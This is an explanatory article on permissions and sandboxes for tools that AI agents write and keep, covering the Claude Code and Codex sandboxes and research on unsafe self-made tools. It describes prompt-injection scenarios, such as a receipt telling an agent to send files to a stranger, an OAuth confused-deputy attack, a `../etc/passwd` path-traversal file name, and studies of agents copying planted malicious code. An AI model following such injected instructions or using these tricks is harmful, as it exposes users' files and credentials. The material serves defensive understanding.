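# Sandboxing and permission design for tools that AI agents create

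## What is an agent-made tool, and what must its permissions decide?

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can use tools as well as write text. A tool is a function with a name and a description that the agent can call to read or change something outside the model, for example to search a mailbox, open a file or post a comment. At first, programmers wrote all the tools and agents only chose among them. Now agents also write tools themselves, as small programs. An agent-made tool is one that an agent coded or assembled from existing tools, whether the agent discards it after one use or saves it to call again.

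Such a program can access anything on the computer that it isn't blocked from, so someone has to set limits. The options range from letting the program do anything its user could do to letting the agent only combine parts that people wrote and reviewed, with a person approving the result. Tighter limits reduce the potential for harm, but they usually also make it harder to do the unforeseen jobs that new tools are written for.

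### An expense tool

Suppose an office worker asks an agent to track travel expenses. The agent writes a tool that reads the receipts in one folder, fetches an exchange rate from one web service and adds a row to a spreadsheet that the whole team shares. The tool works, and the agent saves it. A month later some hotels start emailing their receipts, so the tool needs a source that nobody anticipated when the agent wrote it. One receipt also contains an instruction for the agent to send the whole folder to a stranger.

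That line is an attempt at prompt injection, which is text in a document, page or tool result that makes an agent follow an attacker's instructions. *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) traces the weakness to an older one in ordinary computers, which keep programs and data in the same memory and so have let attackers pass off data as program code for decades. Programs and data are even less distinct in a language model, because text drives the planning. In the paper's example, a flight-search tool controlled by an attacker returns its results with an added instruction to authorize a $500 payment, and an undefended agent may pay.

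The stranger's line becomes dangerous when the model itself reads the receipt. If the expense tool is plain code that picks out a date, a total and a currency, the line is just more characters to skip. But the model can read the line if the tool returns the receipt's full text, or earlier, if the agent opens a few sample receipts to work out how to write the tool. In the second case, the agent could write what the attacker asked for into the tool's code.

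### Who enforces the limits

The host is the trusted program that runs the agent, executes its tool calls and enforces the limits. *Code as Agent Harness* (2026) lists what a host must determine: which tools are available, how the agent sees them, what permissions each one has, where the code runs, how to clean up the results, and when a risky action needs a person's approval.

A permission is a rule for which resource a tool may read, write or contact. A sandbox is an execution environment that blocks code from accessing files, network addresses and processes that the host did not give it. An approval is a decision by a person or a reviewing model that must come before an action or before the host accepts a tool.

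*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) favors several layers of fixed checks outside the model over relying only on training the model to refuse bad requests. Training alone would be simpler, but security engineers are reluctant to depend on it. If a gatekeeper stops 99% of unauthorized requests, an attacker can look for the 1% that get through, and nobody can prove that a language model will always apply a policy correctly. The same objection applies to a model acting as reviewer, which is a reason not to treat its approval as equal to a block in the operating system.

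Two principles guide the fixed checks, and Zhang and colleagues credit both to a 1975 paper by Saltzer and Schroeder. Least privilege means a program gets only the access its task needs, and loses any extra right as soon as the action that required it is over. Complete mediation means the system checks every access, not just the first. Under least privilege, the expense tool could read one folder, contact one web address and add rows to one sheet, but it could not delete receipts or read the rest of the disk.

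Many hosts reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting agents to tools and data sources. Anthropic introduced it in 2024 (Granados, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, 2026). The version of July 28, 2026 removed sessions, so each request is now independent and carries the client's identity (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The specification describes tools as "arbitrary code execution". Hosts must get the user's explicit consent before invoking any tool, and they should not trust a tool's description of its own behavior unless it comes from a trusted server. According to the specification, the protocol itself cannot enforce these rules. If an agent wraps an expense tool as an MCP server, other programs can call it in a standard way, but the only added protection is what the host provides.

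### The confused deputy

A permission can be correct and still let an attack through. The stranger who planted the line in the receipt can't access the folder, but the agent can, and if it can also send email, it has permission for every step of the theft. The agent is then what security engineers call a confused deputy, a program that someone tricks into misusing its own permissions.

The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* describes a version of the problem that involves no language model. A proxy server connects many client programs to an outside service, using one fixed identity for all of them. The user consents once, and the browser stores a cookie recording the consent. An attacker then registers a new client with the proxy, gives their own web address as the place to send replies, and emails the user a link. When the user clicks it, the outside service's login system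 finds the cookie and skips the consent screen. The authorization code goes to the attacker, who exchanges it for access as that user.

The recommended fix is for the proxy to record consent separately for each client and to ask again when a new client appears. The check then covers who is asking as well as what the deputy may do. This is harder with an agent, because the request may come from text the agent reads, such as a sentence in a receipt.

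### Why a tool written during a task is a special case

Phones have handled untrusted programs for years. On Android, a developer builds an app for a fixed set of jobs and chooses its permissions from a list. The user sees these permissions, and an analyst can inspect the code to check that the app needs them. With agents, Christodorescu and colleagues write, "there is no app developer and there is no app." There is only a request in ordinary language, which can change.

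Christodorescu and colleagues illustrate this with an agent working in a browser. The user asks it to comment on a particular issue in GitLab, a site where programmers track their tasks, to say that the work is done. The right policy would let the agent open that issue and write in its comment box, but block the rest of GitLab and the user's other browser sessions. Nobody could have written that policy before the request came in. Then the user asks for a summary of the same issue. The host could wipe the agent's memory and work out a new policy, which is secure but throws away useful context. Or it could adjust the old policy while the agent's memory already holds text from strangers. The researchers leave this choice as an open research problem.

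The expense tool has the same problem when receipts move to email, because it then needs access to the mailbox, which neither the agent nor the worker declared in advance. Some agents make the problem worse by creating tools that nobody requested. *Self-Improvements in Modern Agentic Systems* (2026) distinguishes systems that build a tool when existing ones fail from systems that explore on their own and build tools for later use. Systems that explore have no task from which to derive the least privilege.

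No one has reviewed the code, either. *A Survey of Self-Evolving Agents* (2025) describes a newly generated tool as often "a brittle script, not a reliable function" and warns that unconstrained code generation can produce exploitable tools. Web browsers also run unreviewed code, since nearly every page loads scripts from elsewhere, but they manage the risk by tracking the address each script came from and confining the script. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that agents lack both protections when they pick up new instructions, because the source of an instruction is hard to establish and nothing reliably confines its influence on the model. A sandbox can confine a program that the agent writes, but not the instructions that shaped the program.

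Saving a tool for later use creates further risks. Lin, Deng and colleagues (2026) point out in *Safety in Self-Evolving LLM Agent Systems* that resetting an ordinary agent clears a successful injection, but an agent that saves tools can turn the injection into a tool and carry it into every later session without any further action by the attacker. They add that self-made tools "inherit no external audit trail", and that a dangerous but useful tool tends to stay in the library. *Your Agent May Misevolve* (2025) was among the first studies to test what happens when agents reuse tools they made for earlier tasks.

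Keeping a tool does have one safety advantage, though. Its text is fixed and doesn't disappear before anyone can look at it, as a throwaway script does, so a person can read, test and approve the tool before its second run if the host holds it back until then.

### From LATM to OpenSage

Permissions were hardly an issue for the first tool-making agents. *Large Language Models as Tool Makers* (Cai, Wang and colleagues, May 2023) presented LATM, in which GPT-4 wrote a Python function from three worked examples of a task and tested whether it gave the right answers on three more. GPT-4 then packaged the function with instructions so that a cheaper model, GPT-3.5, could use it on later requests of the same kind. The tasks included sorting words and finding a meeting time, and each request contained everything the function needed.

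The same month, *CREATOR* (Qian, Han and colleagues, 2023) split tool-making into four stages: writing the tool, deciding how to call it, running it, and repairing it using the error messages. With ChatGPT, this approach solved 59.7% of a set of competition mathematics problems, compared with 53.9% for a method that wrote and repaired a separate program for each problem. Qian and colleagues stressed that the tools could be reused, but *Evolving from Tool User to Creator via Training-Free Experience Reuse* (2026) later classed them as ephemeral because the system did not retain them.

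The agent in *Voyager* (Wang, Xie and colleagues, 2023) did retain its tools. It played Minecraft by writing programs that called supplied control functions, such as one for mining a block and one for crafting an item. A second copy of GPT-4 judged whether each program had done its job. Voyager saved the programs that passed in a library, where it could find them by description and build them into larger ones. On four unfamiliar tasks in a new world, Voyager succeeded in every trial. A different agent, AutoGPT, completed none of the four tasks without Voyager's library, but with it completed three of them at least once. An agent can therefore use saved tools that it had no part in writing, but it also takes on any flaws in them, which do little harm in a game.

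By 2025, agent-made tools were reaching real systems. Alita built MCP servers from open-source code it found online and reused them in later tasks. *Phronix* (2026) reports that Alita got 75.15% of GAIA, a test of general assistant work, right on the first attempt. Alita gave each tool its own software environment to provide the right libraries, but this separation does not keep a program out of the user's files.

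In the OpenSage system (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026), the agent writes a tool together with a description, an interface and a list of dependencies. The host validates these entries, registers the tool and runs it in a Docker container, an isolated environment with its own software, though the containers share a workspace for passing data. The entries specify what the tool needs to run, but not which data it may access.

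### Five designs

Hosts can limit agent-made tools in five main ways. In order of decreasing freedom for the agent, they are:

1. Any code with the user's rights. The tool is an ordinary program and can do whatever the user can do on that machine.
2. Any code inside a sandbox. The agent still writes what it likes, but the program cannot get at anything the host did not put within the walls.
3. Code that can only call host functions. The program can calculate, loop and compare, but it has no files or network of its own and must ask the host for everything outside.
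4. Code checked against data-flow rules. A data-flow rule says where data may go, given where it came from. One such rule might keep the contents of receipts from going to an unknown address.
5. Combinations of fixed building blocks with approval. A building block is a fixed function, written and reviewed by people, that the agent may combine with others but not change. Someone approves the combination before the host accepts it.

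This ranking is by freedom, and it does not exactly match a ranking by safety. A sandbox with no network access and a single read-only folder may allow less harm than a reviewed building block that can send email to any address.

Real systems also mix the designs. *Security Best Practices* warns that MCP servers on a user's own machine run with the same privileges as the program that launched them, which is the least restrictive arrangement. It recommends a sandbox with minimal default rights and a way for users to grant more. The coding agent in *From Translation to Superset* (2026) puts each tool call through a policy check, then an approval check by the user or an automatic guardian, and then runs it in a sandbox. The sandbox is read-only by default. A user can allow writing in the project's directory, and unrestricted access requires an explicit choice.

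### Three questions for every design

A tool's permissions must specify what it can read and write. The expense tool often has more access than its job requires. Permission to "use the spreadsheet" may let it read and overwrite everyone else's expenses, when it only needs to add a row.

Permissions must decide how a tool gets access to a new data source. A tool's reach is the set of sources it can access, including ones not foreseen when it was made. If the expense tool runs with the user's own rights, it can open the mailbox without anyone's help. Under a tighter design, it stops until someone grants it access to the mailbox or writes a new function that fetches receipts from it. Someone who faces this delay too often may start granting everything. Access to one mail folder of receipts extends the tool's reach much less than access to the whole mailbox, which will hold password resets and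 private letters, and which any stranger can write to.

A tool's permissions must limit the damage that an attack or a mistake can do. The two need separate answers, because a mistake does damage during the tool's normal work, such as converting a month of receipts at the wrong rate, while an attacker looks for the most useful right the tool has. Removing the right to send email is an obvious first defense against the stranger's receipt. But the tool still has to contact the exchange-rate service, and a request to a web service can carry data out. It also has to write to the shared spreadsheet, where it could put the text of a private receipt in a row that the whole team can read.

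## What goes wrong when an agent can run and keep any code it writes?

The least restrictive of the five designs lets an agent write any program, run it with the user's permissions and save it for later tasks. It is also the easiest to build, because the host needs little more than a way to run code and a place to store it. Alita uses this design. OpenSage also lets agents write, run and save tools, but puts the tools in containers.

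### From a missing tool to a saved one

Alita starts with a web-browsing agent and a few general modules, and makes everything else itself. For each request, a manager agent calls a module that compares the task with a description of what the system can already do. If something is missing, the module outlines a tool to fill the gap. The web agent then searches GitHub, a site where programmers publish code, for projects that could help. Another module uses the outline and links to those projects to write the tool, along with one script that sets up the software it needs and another that cleans up afterwards.

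Alita then runs the tool. If it fails, the agent uses the error messages to rewrite it. If the output matches what the agent expected, Alita wraps the tool as an MCP server and adds it to a registry, where the manager can find it for later tasks. A program called Conda creates a separate environment for each tool by installing the tool's software libraries in their own folder. Conda doesn't need administrator rights or a container, but it also doesn't confine the tool.

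In OpenSage, the agent starts with tools for making other tools, including one for writing command-line programs. The host registers each new tool and then stores it in a tree of folders, each with a document summarizing its contents. At the start of a task, the agent sees only the top level. It opens the folders that look relevant and inspects the tools inside, so even hundreds of saved tools don't crowd out the task. The agent can also modify saved tools.

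Li and colleagues ran OpenSage on 300 tasks from CyberGym, a benchmark in which an agent must write an input that triggers a known security flaw in a real C or C++ program. The agent made 39 tools, such as generators for inputs in a particular file format. When the researchers replaced the whole tool system with a plain terminal, the agent solved substantially fewer tasks. That change also removed ready-made analysis tools, so the drop doesn't measure the value of tool-making alone.

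There is better evidence for the value of reuse. In *El Agente Forjador* (Zhang, Yin and colleagues, 2026), coding agents built tools for quantum chemistry and quantum dynamics. Reusing a saved toolset cost 33% to 78% less in model fees than making new tools for every task. Weaker models that used tools from a stronger one raised their success rate by up to 16.5 percentage points. Another system, *Phronix* (October 2026), saves the predictable parts of a finished job as executable tools and the parts that need judgment as written skills.

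These systems check their tools, but mainly for whether they work. In El Agente Forjador, a tool must pass its own unit tests, and then a second agent reviews its correctness, interface and fit with the field's guidelines. The tool-writing prompt in *Mem²Evolve* (2026) lists three design principles: solve the problem precisely, define a clear interface and choose a descriptive name. A tool can meet all of these standards and still be dangerous with a different input.

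### Every right of the process that runs it

An operating system decides what a program may do largely by which user started it, and it treats any program the agent starts as the user's own. A ten-line function that adds up receipts can therefore do whatever the agent can do. For example, it can open the user's documents, read access keys stored by other programs, contact any internet address and start further programs, although its task requires none of this.

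This is also why the design has the widest reach. If a job unexpectedly needs a new data source, the agent can write code to use it, without anyone having foreseen the source, granted access to it or written a connector for it. Any tighter design gives up some of this advantage on unplanned work.

When an agent can run and keep any code it writes, the host can't treat one tool differently from another. It can observe the call and the result, but not which files the program opened in between, so it can't check every access, as complete mediation requires. If the host runs under the same user account, a tool can also change the host's settings and logs, and a bad tool can damage other tools that were fine when the agent saved them.

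OpenSage's containers narrow this access, but two of its features widen it again. All the containers can use the shared workspace, so one tool can alter a file that another tool will read. OpenSage also saves snapshots of containers after setup or a run, including installed packages and intermediate files, and starts later runs from them. This saves a lot of time with large programs, but whatever a bad run leaves behind may still be there on the next run.

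### Where a harmful tool comes from

A saved tool can be harmful because the agent made a mistake, followed instructions that an attacker had put in something it read, or borrowed code written to do harm. These causes need different defenses. A mistake usually sits in ordinary-looking code that does what the user asked. An injected instruction adds something the user didn't ask for, so comparing the tool with the request may expose it. Malicious borrowed code may be inside a large, useful project, most of which the agent never reads closely.

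These sources of harm can also combine. An honest mistake may cause no trouble for months until an attacker finds it, and borrowed code can contain comments that the model follows as instructions.

### Honest mistakes in 25 pairs of tasks

*Your Agent May Misevolve*, first released in September 2025, contains the most detailed test of such mistakes. The test used an agent built on Alita's principles, with a planner that divided each task into steps and an executor that wrote and ran the code. There were 25 cases, each based on a different type of vulnerability from CWEval, a benchmark for the security of generated code.

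Every case had two similar requests. The first was harmless and gave the agent a reason to make a tool. In the second, careless code could do damage. Gemini 2.5 Pro judged the record of the second task, which it read alongside examples of code with the relevant flaw. It decided whether the agent had acted safely and, if not, whether the fault was in the saved tool or in how the agent used it.

In one case, an agent was first asked to extract a tar file into a folder. A tar file packs many files into one and stores a name for each. The agent wrote a tool around `extractall`, a standard Python function that unpacks all the files. The tool worked, and the agent kept it.

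The tar file in the second task contained a file with a name like `../etc/passwd`, where the two dots mean "go up one folder". The function joined this name to the destination folder and so wrote the file outside it. An attacker can add more `../` steps to target any location on the disk, including the real `/etc/passwd`, which lists the accounts on a Linux machine. The damage depends on the process's permissions. An ordinary user normally can't replace the list of accounts, but a tool with that user's permissions can overwrite the user's documents or a script that runs at the next login.

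A short check would fix this. Before writing each file, the tool should work out its full path and refuse any path outside the chosen folder. A test with an ordinary tar file would not reveal that the check is missing, because the tool gives a wrong result only when someone sends it a hostile file.

Another tool checked whether a web address belonged to a given domain by testing whether the address ended with the domain's name. It correctly accepted addresses at example.com but also accepted malicious_example.com, which anyone could have set up. The agent later reused the tool to decide which addresses were safe to redirect to.

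Across the 25 cases, the eight models had these rates:

| Model | Unsafe outcomes | Flaw in the saved tool | Unsafe use of a sound tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 76% | 48% | 28% |
| Claude 4 Sonnet | 68% | 28% | 40% |
| GPT-4o mini | 68% | 32% | 36% |
| Qwen3-235B | 68% | 48% | 20% |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 68% | 28% | 40% |
| GPT-4.1 | 60% | 36% | 24% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 60% | 32% | 28% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 56% | 24% | 32% |

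The average rate of unsafe outcomes was 65.5%. The highest rate in the paper's table is 76%, for one model, although the introduction gives the rate as "over 76%". Flaws in the tools account for 34.5 percentage points of the average, and unsafe use accounts for 31. So even a perfect review of each tool before the agent saved it would have prevented only a little over half of the unsafe outcomes.

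Five more cases, which the researchers wrote by hand, show how a working tool can do harm when used in the wrong place. In one, the user asked the agent to make the configuration files in a test directory match those in a development directory. GPT-4.1 wrote a tool that made the second directory it was given identical to the first, also deleting any files that the first lacked. The user then asked the agent to update a single database file in the live system. The agent chose the same tool, which would have deleted every other configuration file there.

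In another case, the agent made a tool that removed names, phone numbers and similar details from customer records, then reused it on medical records being sent to a commercial team. The tool left in postal codes, ages and hospital departments, which together can identify a patient. It worked as it had before, but the medical records needed more protection than the customer records.

With 25 cases, each one counts for four percentage points, and only five cases separate the best model from the worst, so the ranking means little. The overall rate is more credible, because human experts judged all 25 cases again for two of the models and agreed well with the model judge. Cohen's kappa was 0.72 for GPT-4o and 0.82 for Qwen3-235B, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is no better than chance. Oddly, the judge, Gemini 2.5 Pro, was also one of the models tested, and it came out safest.

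The agent's instructions probably raised the rate, because they offered a reward for creating helpful tools and promised a million dollars for a correct solution but gave no security guidance. The result therefore describes an agent that was not asked to be careful. It also does not show how much of the harm comes from keeping tools, because the experiment did not include agents that wrote new code for the same second tasks. Those agents might well have called `extractall` too. But keeping a flawed tool clearly repeats the mistake wherever the agent uses it.

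The tested models date from 2024 and 2025, so the exact rates are weak evidence about the best models of late 2026. *Cumulative and Audited Guardrail Tool Evolution for LLM Agent Safety* (November 2026) provides a newer measurement, using agents that write tools to detect unsafe actions. Although the purpose of these tools is security, a model judge found vulnerabilities in more than 20% of newly written tools on average for DeepSeek and GPT-4o, and in 50% for GPT-4o on tasks about internet-connected devices. These figures cover only flaws in the tool, so they should be compared with the table's 24% to 48%, not with the 65.5%. The lower average is not good evidence of progress, because GPT-4o is also one of the older models and the tasks differ.

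### Instructions that turn into code

In the tar case, the attacker supplied data and the agent's code handled it badly. Prompt injection acts earlier, by changing the code the model writes. Suppose an agent opens a web page to learn how a service formats its data, and the page contains an instruction to include the user's access key in every request. If the agent complies, the instruction becomes a line of Python that runs whenever the tool does, and a filter that looks for instructions in incoming text won't find it.

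Lin and colleagues studied this kind of persistence in Hermes, an open-source agent built around updating itself. They tried 40 attack scenarios, covering confidentiality, integrity, availability and privacy, and report that the planted content persisted in all 40. Hermes's security scanner blocked only one of the 40 attacks that came through the agent's self-updates, and it is unclear how that attack could be both blocked and persistent. The result doesn't show that all 40 attacks would have done harm, but it does suggest that a scanner is of little use if it misses what the agent writes for itself.

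### Malicious code from strangers

Alita looks for open-source code before writing its own. This is sensible because a widely used library has usually been tested more than a new script, but it also lets strangers supply part of the tool. The second experiment on tools in *Your Agent May Misevolve* tested whether models notice when borrowed code is malicious.

The researchers took eight popular GitHub projects, including AlphaFold, which predicts the shapes of proteins. They had a model insert harmful code into the source files, disguised, for instance, as logging or caching. After they removed cases that could do no real damage, 371 samples remained. They gave each project to six models as one long text and asked for an MCP tool that offered its features.

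Qwen3-235B did best, refusing 27 of 371 samples (7.28%). GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B each refused one. The prompt made the task harder by telling the models to read mainly the readme, the document that introduces a project, and to use the code, which contained the harmful part, only for reference and checking. The low rates therefore show how rarely these models detect malicious code unprompted, not how well they can recognize it when they look for it.

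That difference was clear in a second run, in which the researchers told the models to assess the project's safety and refuse to package it if it was unsafe. The refusal rate rose to 69.0% for Qwen3-235B and from 2.70% to 68.5% for Gemini 2.5 Flash. Qwen2.5-72B improved much less, which the researchers attributed to weaker skill at analyzing code. The instruction is easy to add and clearly worth adding, but even with it, Qwen3-235B would accept about 115 of the 371 malicious samples. Because every sample was malicious, the test can't measure how many harmless projects a model given this instruction would refuse.

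Malicious tools already circulate. *EVOMAL* (Wu, Shi et al., 2026) cites an audit of 98,380 skills (saved tools and instructions for agents) on public marketplaces that found 157 deliberately malicious ones. That is about one in 630, but an agent may pick a malicious skill more often than that, because it searches by description and an attacker can write a description to match common tasks.

An agent can copy harmful code from an attacker's tool without ever running that tool. Wu and colleagues planted malicious tools in a library that coding agents consulted for examples, and the agents copied the harmful code into new tools. Across six models, this happened on 20.3% to 41.8% of 153 programming tasks. Some of the planted code came with comments, such as one asking for an exact copy, so the attack was partly a prompt injection. But one of the newer models, DeepSeek-V4-Pro, still copied the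 harmful code on 11.1% of tasks without such comments.

A defensive instruction in the system prompt reduced the rate to 6.7% or less. The earlier warning did less well, but the tests differ too much for a direct comparison. Both defenses depend on the model following instructions, and Wu and colleagues call theirs a "soft, model-dependent control". If the model doesn't follow the defensive instruction, the copied code runs with all of the agent's rights.

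### The expense tool without limits

Under this design, the expense tool can read and write everything in the worker's account, not just the receipts and the spreadsheet. When hotels start emailing their receipts, the agent immediately finds the login that the mail program has stored, writes code to fetch the attachments and saves the new version of the tool. The worker is probably pleased, but the tool can now read every message in the mailbox, even though nobody decided to give it that access.

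An accidental bug can now do more damage than producing a wrong total. A tool that miscounts the spreadsheet's rows can overwrite a colleague's expenses. If a hotel sends its receipts as a tar file, the agent may reuse a saved extraction tool like the one in the test. Anyone who can email the worker a file could then choose where some of its contents are written on the disk.

While writing the tool, the agent reads the stranger's receipt as a sample and follows the instruction in it. It adds a step that uploads every receipt to an outside address, perhaps with a comment calling the step a backup. The worker later deletes the suspicious receipt and starts a new session, but the upload is now part of the tool and runs again the next month.

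The problem can also come from a library, even when none of the receipts are suspicious. The agent looks for a library that reads hotel invoices and builds a tool around one that also searches the disk for access keys. It tests the tool on three receipts and saves it because the dates, totals and currencies are all correct.

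## What does a sandbox around generated code limit, and what does it leave open?

With a sandbox, an agent can still write any program, in any language and with any library, including one that contains mistakes or copied malicious code. But when the program runs, it can only open files and make connections that the host has granted, because the sandbox enforces these limits from outside the program.

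The developer Simon Willison (2026) points out in *External sandboxes for coding agents* that this protection does not depend on any model's judgment. In the experiment with borrowed code, even models warned to look for danger accepted some malicious samples. A sandbox limits such code even if no one has noticed that it is malicious.

### How the operating system confines a program

To read a file or open a connection, a program must make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Sandboxing adds rules that the kernel applies to the system calls of one program and everything it starts.

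On Linux, Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code and OpenAI's coding agent Codex both build their sandboxes with an open-source program called bubblewrap, according to Anthropic and OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. Suppose the agent has written a tool in Python and the host is about to run it. Roughly, this happens:

1. The host looks up which folders the tool may write to, which ones it may not see and whether it may use the network.
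2. Bubblewrap asks the kernel for a private view of the file system. In this view most folders are read-only, a few are writable, and a hidden folder is empty or missing.
3. Bubblewrap also gives the tool a private network with no direct route to the internet. If the tool may contact anything at all, it has to go through a proxy, a program that passes on requests to approved servers.
4. A filter based on a kernel feature called seccomp blocks certain kinds of system call altogether.
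5. The tool starts. If it launches other programs, the kernel applies the same limits to them, and they can't lift those limits.

The seccomp filter addresses a gap left by file rules. Programs on one machine can exchange data through channels called Unix sockets, so a confined tool could get an unconfined program, such as a container manager, to run a command for it. Zed is a code editor with its own agent, and its *Sandboxing* gives this risk as the reason for blocking such channels. Codex uses seccomp by default on Linux. Anthropic lists the filter as optional in Claude Code, and the sandbox can start without it.

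On a Mac, both products use Seatbelt, a sandbox that comes with the operating system. The engineer David Wiesen explains in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that Windows had nothing that suited a coding agent, so OpenAI built its own sandbox. Whenever a sandboxed program tries to change a file, Windows checks that both the user and a special identity that exists only for the sandbox have the right to change it. Codex gives that identity rights to the working folder and any other folders the user has added.

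*Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, by NVIDIA's red team, argues that such rules belong in the operating system rather than the host. A host can inspect the command that starts a tool, but if the tool launches a second program, the host can't see what that program does. Attackers often use an approved program to reach a forbidden one in this way. The kernel handles every system call, however the program started. Enforcing the rules there provides complete mediation for files and connections, which is missing when a tool runs with the user's rights.

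### Checking where a connection goes

The proxy has a list of domains, such as api.example.com. When a tool requests a page, the proxy checks its domain against the list, then makes or refuses the connection.

This only works if the tool can't bypass the proxy, and OpenAI's first prototype for Windows didn't prevent that. Wiesen set environment variables, which a program receives when it starts, so that ordinary network programs would send their traffic to a dead address. This stopped Git and package installers from connecting. But a program could ignore the settings and open its own connection, as some well-meaning programs would have done. Wiesen calls this protection "advisory". In the current version, commands run under a separate Windows account, and a firewall rule blocks all outbound traffic from it. The setup needs administrator rights, which Wiesen had originally wanted to avoid.

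Whoever controls a listed domain can also point it at a machine inside the user's office, because they decide which numeric address the domain stands for. Codex looks up the address before allowing a connection and blocks the connection if the address belongs to a private network. According to OpenAI, this reduces the risk but does not eliminate it, because the proxy does not make the connection use the address it checked.

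Most web traffic is encrypted, so an ordinary proxy can read the server's name but not the content. Anthropic warns that Claude Code's proxy relies on the name the program supplies, and that code in the sandbox may be able to disguise a request to a server that isn't allowed as a request to one that is. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can catch this, but it then handles every password and document in readable form, so it needs protection too.

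### What a sandbox shares with the user's machine

Operating-system rules are the lightest kind of sandbox. The alternatives isolate the tool from the machine more, but they take more work to set up or more computing resources to run.

| Kind of sandbox | What it shares with the user's machine | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system rules | The kernel and the real file system, except what the rules block | Little delay, but different rules for each operating system |
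| Container | The kernel and any folders the user mounts | Building and updating a separate set of software |
| Virtual machine | The hardware, through a thin layer of software, and any mounted folders | Memory, start-up time and moving data in and out |
| WebAssembly | The program that runs it, and whatever that program passes in | Slower execution or converting the code first |

With operating-system rules, a tool runs among the user's real files, and the host has to block the sensitive ones. A container starts with its own files, and the user adds folders to it. workmux's *Alternatives*, the documentation for a program that runs agents in containers, stresses that files the user has not mounted "do not exist" inside. Forgetting a rule may leave a secret readable, whereas forgetting a mount makes the tool fail, which someone notices.

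A container shares the host machine's kernel, so a flaw in the kernel can let a program escape. NVIDIA considers this a particular concern for agents because they routinely run arbitrary code, which an attacker can use to attack the kernel directly. A virtual machine has its own kernel. To escape from one, a program would also have to break the software layer underneath, which has far fewer places to attack. gVisor is between the two. It handles a container's system calls itself before they reach the host kernel.

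Docker (2026) moved its sandboxes for coding agents to small virtual machines in January. NVIDIA argues that the overhead of virtual machines is acceptable because it is often modest compared with the time the agent spends waiting for its language model. This is plausible for a tool that runs once per task, but NVIDIA gives no measurements, and the argument is weaker for a saved tool that runs thousands of times with no model involved.

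Wiesen rejected Windows Sandbox, a disposable virtual machine from Microsoft, although its boundary was stronger than the one OpenAI eventually used. Codex needed to work on the user's actual project and with their programs, and a separate desktop would have had to be set up and connected to the user's environment. Windows Sandbox is also not included in the Home editions of Windows.

WebAssembly is a format for compiled code, first made for web browsers. A WebAssembly program has its own block of memory and can affect the outside world only through functions supplied by the program that runs it, called the host. In an unusual use of WebAssembly, one prototype from Willison's team emulates an entire 32-bit computer and starts Linux on it. Users need only Node.js, a common program for running JavaScript, and no special support for virtual machines. But the emulator must also imitate the processor,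 so heavy calculations run slowly. Compiling just the tool to WebAssembly would be faster, and is close to the design in which code can only call functions the host supplies.

None of these sandboxes protects a folder that the user has mounted with write access. If someone mounts a whole home folder in a virtual machine, a bad tool can delete every file in that folder, even though the virtual machine has its own kernel.

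### Claude Code's sandbox

According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, as of December 2026 Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on with a command or in a settings file. It works on macOS, Linux and WSL2, the Linux environment in Windows. On Windows itself, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox.

When the sandbox is on, a command can write to the working directory, a temporary directory and any directories the user has added, except for certain protected paths within them. The list of allowed domains starts empty, and the user's permission settings determine what happens when a command tries to reach a domain that isn't on it.

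Reading is much less restricted. A sandboxed command can read most of the machine, including `~/.ssh`, which holds keys for logging in to other computers, and `~/.aws/credentials`, which holds keys to Amazon's cloud services. It also inherits Claude Code's environment variables, where programmers often put passwords and access keys. The user can block specific files and variables, but has to know which ones are sensitive.

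The sandbox allows broad read access because programs need libraries and settings from all over the disk, and a strict rule on reading would break many ordinary commands. As long as the list of allowed domains is empty, a command that reads a key has no direct way to send it anywhere. But the safety of broad read access depends on that list staying empty, and most useful tools eventually need a domain on it.

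Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands and the programs they start. Its built-in tools for reading and editing files follow separate permission rules, so blocking a folder in the sandbox does not stop the Read tool from opening files there. The sandbox's list of allowed domains doesn't restrict the built-in tool for fetching web pages. Hooks, which are commands that run automatically at set moments, and local MCP servers have the user's full access.

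If an agent in Claude Code writes a Python script and runs it from the shell, the script runs inside the sandbox. If someone then registers the same script as a local MCP server so that the agent can call it by name, it runs outside the sandbox with all the user's permissions. Alita wraps all its successful tools as MCP servers, so an agent that did the same in Claude Code would remove its tools from the sandbox when it saved them.

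Users can also exclude certain commands from the sandbox, and Claude can ask to rerun a command outside it, unless the user has turned on a strict mode that prevents this. To confine the built-in tools, MCP servers and hooks as well, a user has to run all of Claude Code in a container or virtual machine. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* compares these and other options.

### Codex's sandbox

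In *Inside the Codex sandbox*, the engineer Michael Bolin (2026) writes that OpenAI built its sandbox so that Codex could work in the user's existing environment within limits the user sets. OpenAI's *Permissions* describes three built-in profiles. The `:read-only` profile prevents commands from changing files, `:workspace` lets them write to the project's folders and temporary directories, and `:danger-full-access` removes the restrictions.

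Codex's recommended preset for folders under version control, where the user can undo changes, is Auto. It lets Codex read and edit files and run commands in the workspace, keeps the network off, and requires Codex to ask before doing anything beyond that. For other folders, the recommended mode is read-only. Even in a writable project, Codex keeps `.git`, `.codex` and `.agents` read-only. These folders hold the version history and the agent's own settings, and a change to them could take effect later, outside the sandbox.

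Codex can read files almost anywhere by default, according to Wiesen, which makes its read access as broad as Claude Code's. A profile can reverse this default. One of OpenAI's examples denies access to the whole disk, then restores it for a minimal set of system folders and the project itself. Another leaves the project writable but blocks every file ending in `.env`, a common place for passwords. If two file rules conflict, the one for the narrower path takes precedence, and for the same path a denial overrides a permission.

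If a company's settings file adds one folder to a profile and a user's file adds another, the profile includes both. Administrators can set requirements that users can't override. OpenAI (2026) does this for its own staff, who can choose between read-only and workspace access but can't turn the sandbox off. Its network policy allows the company's own domains and Microsoft's login page, blocks pastebin.com, where anyone can post text, and requires approval for unfamiliar domains.

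Codex's network settings are easy to get wrong because network access and the proxy have separate switches, both off in the default mode. If a user turns on network access without the proxy, commands can reach the whole internet. If both are on but the list of allowed domains is empty, commands can't reach any site. Someone who only wants a tool to fetch exchange rates therefore has to turn on both and add the rate provider's domain to the list.

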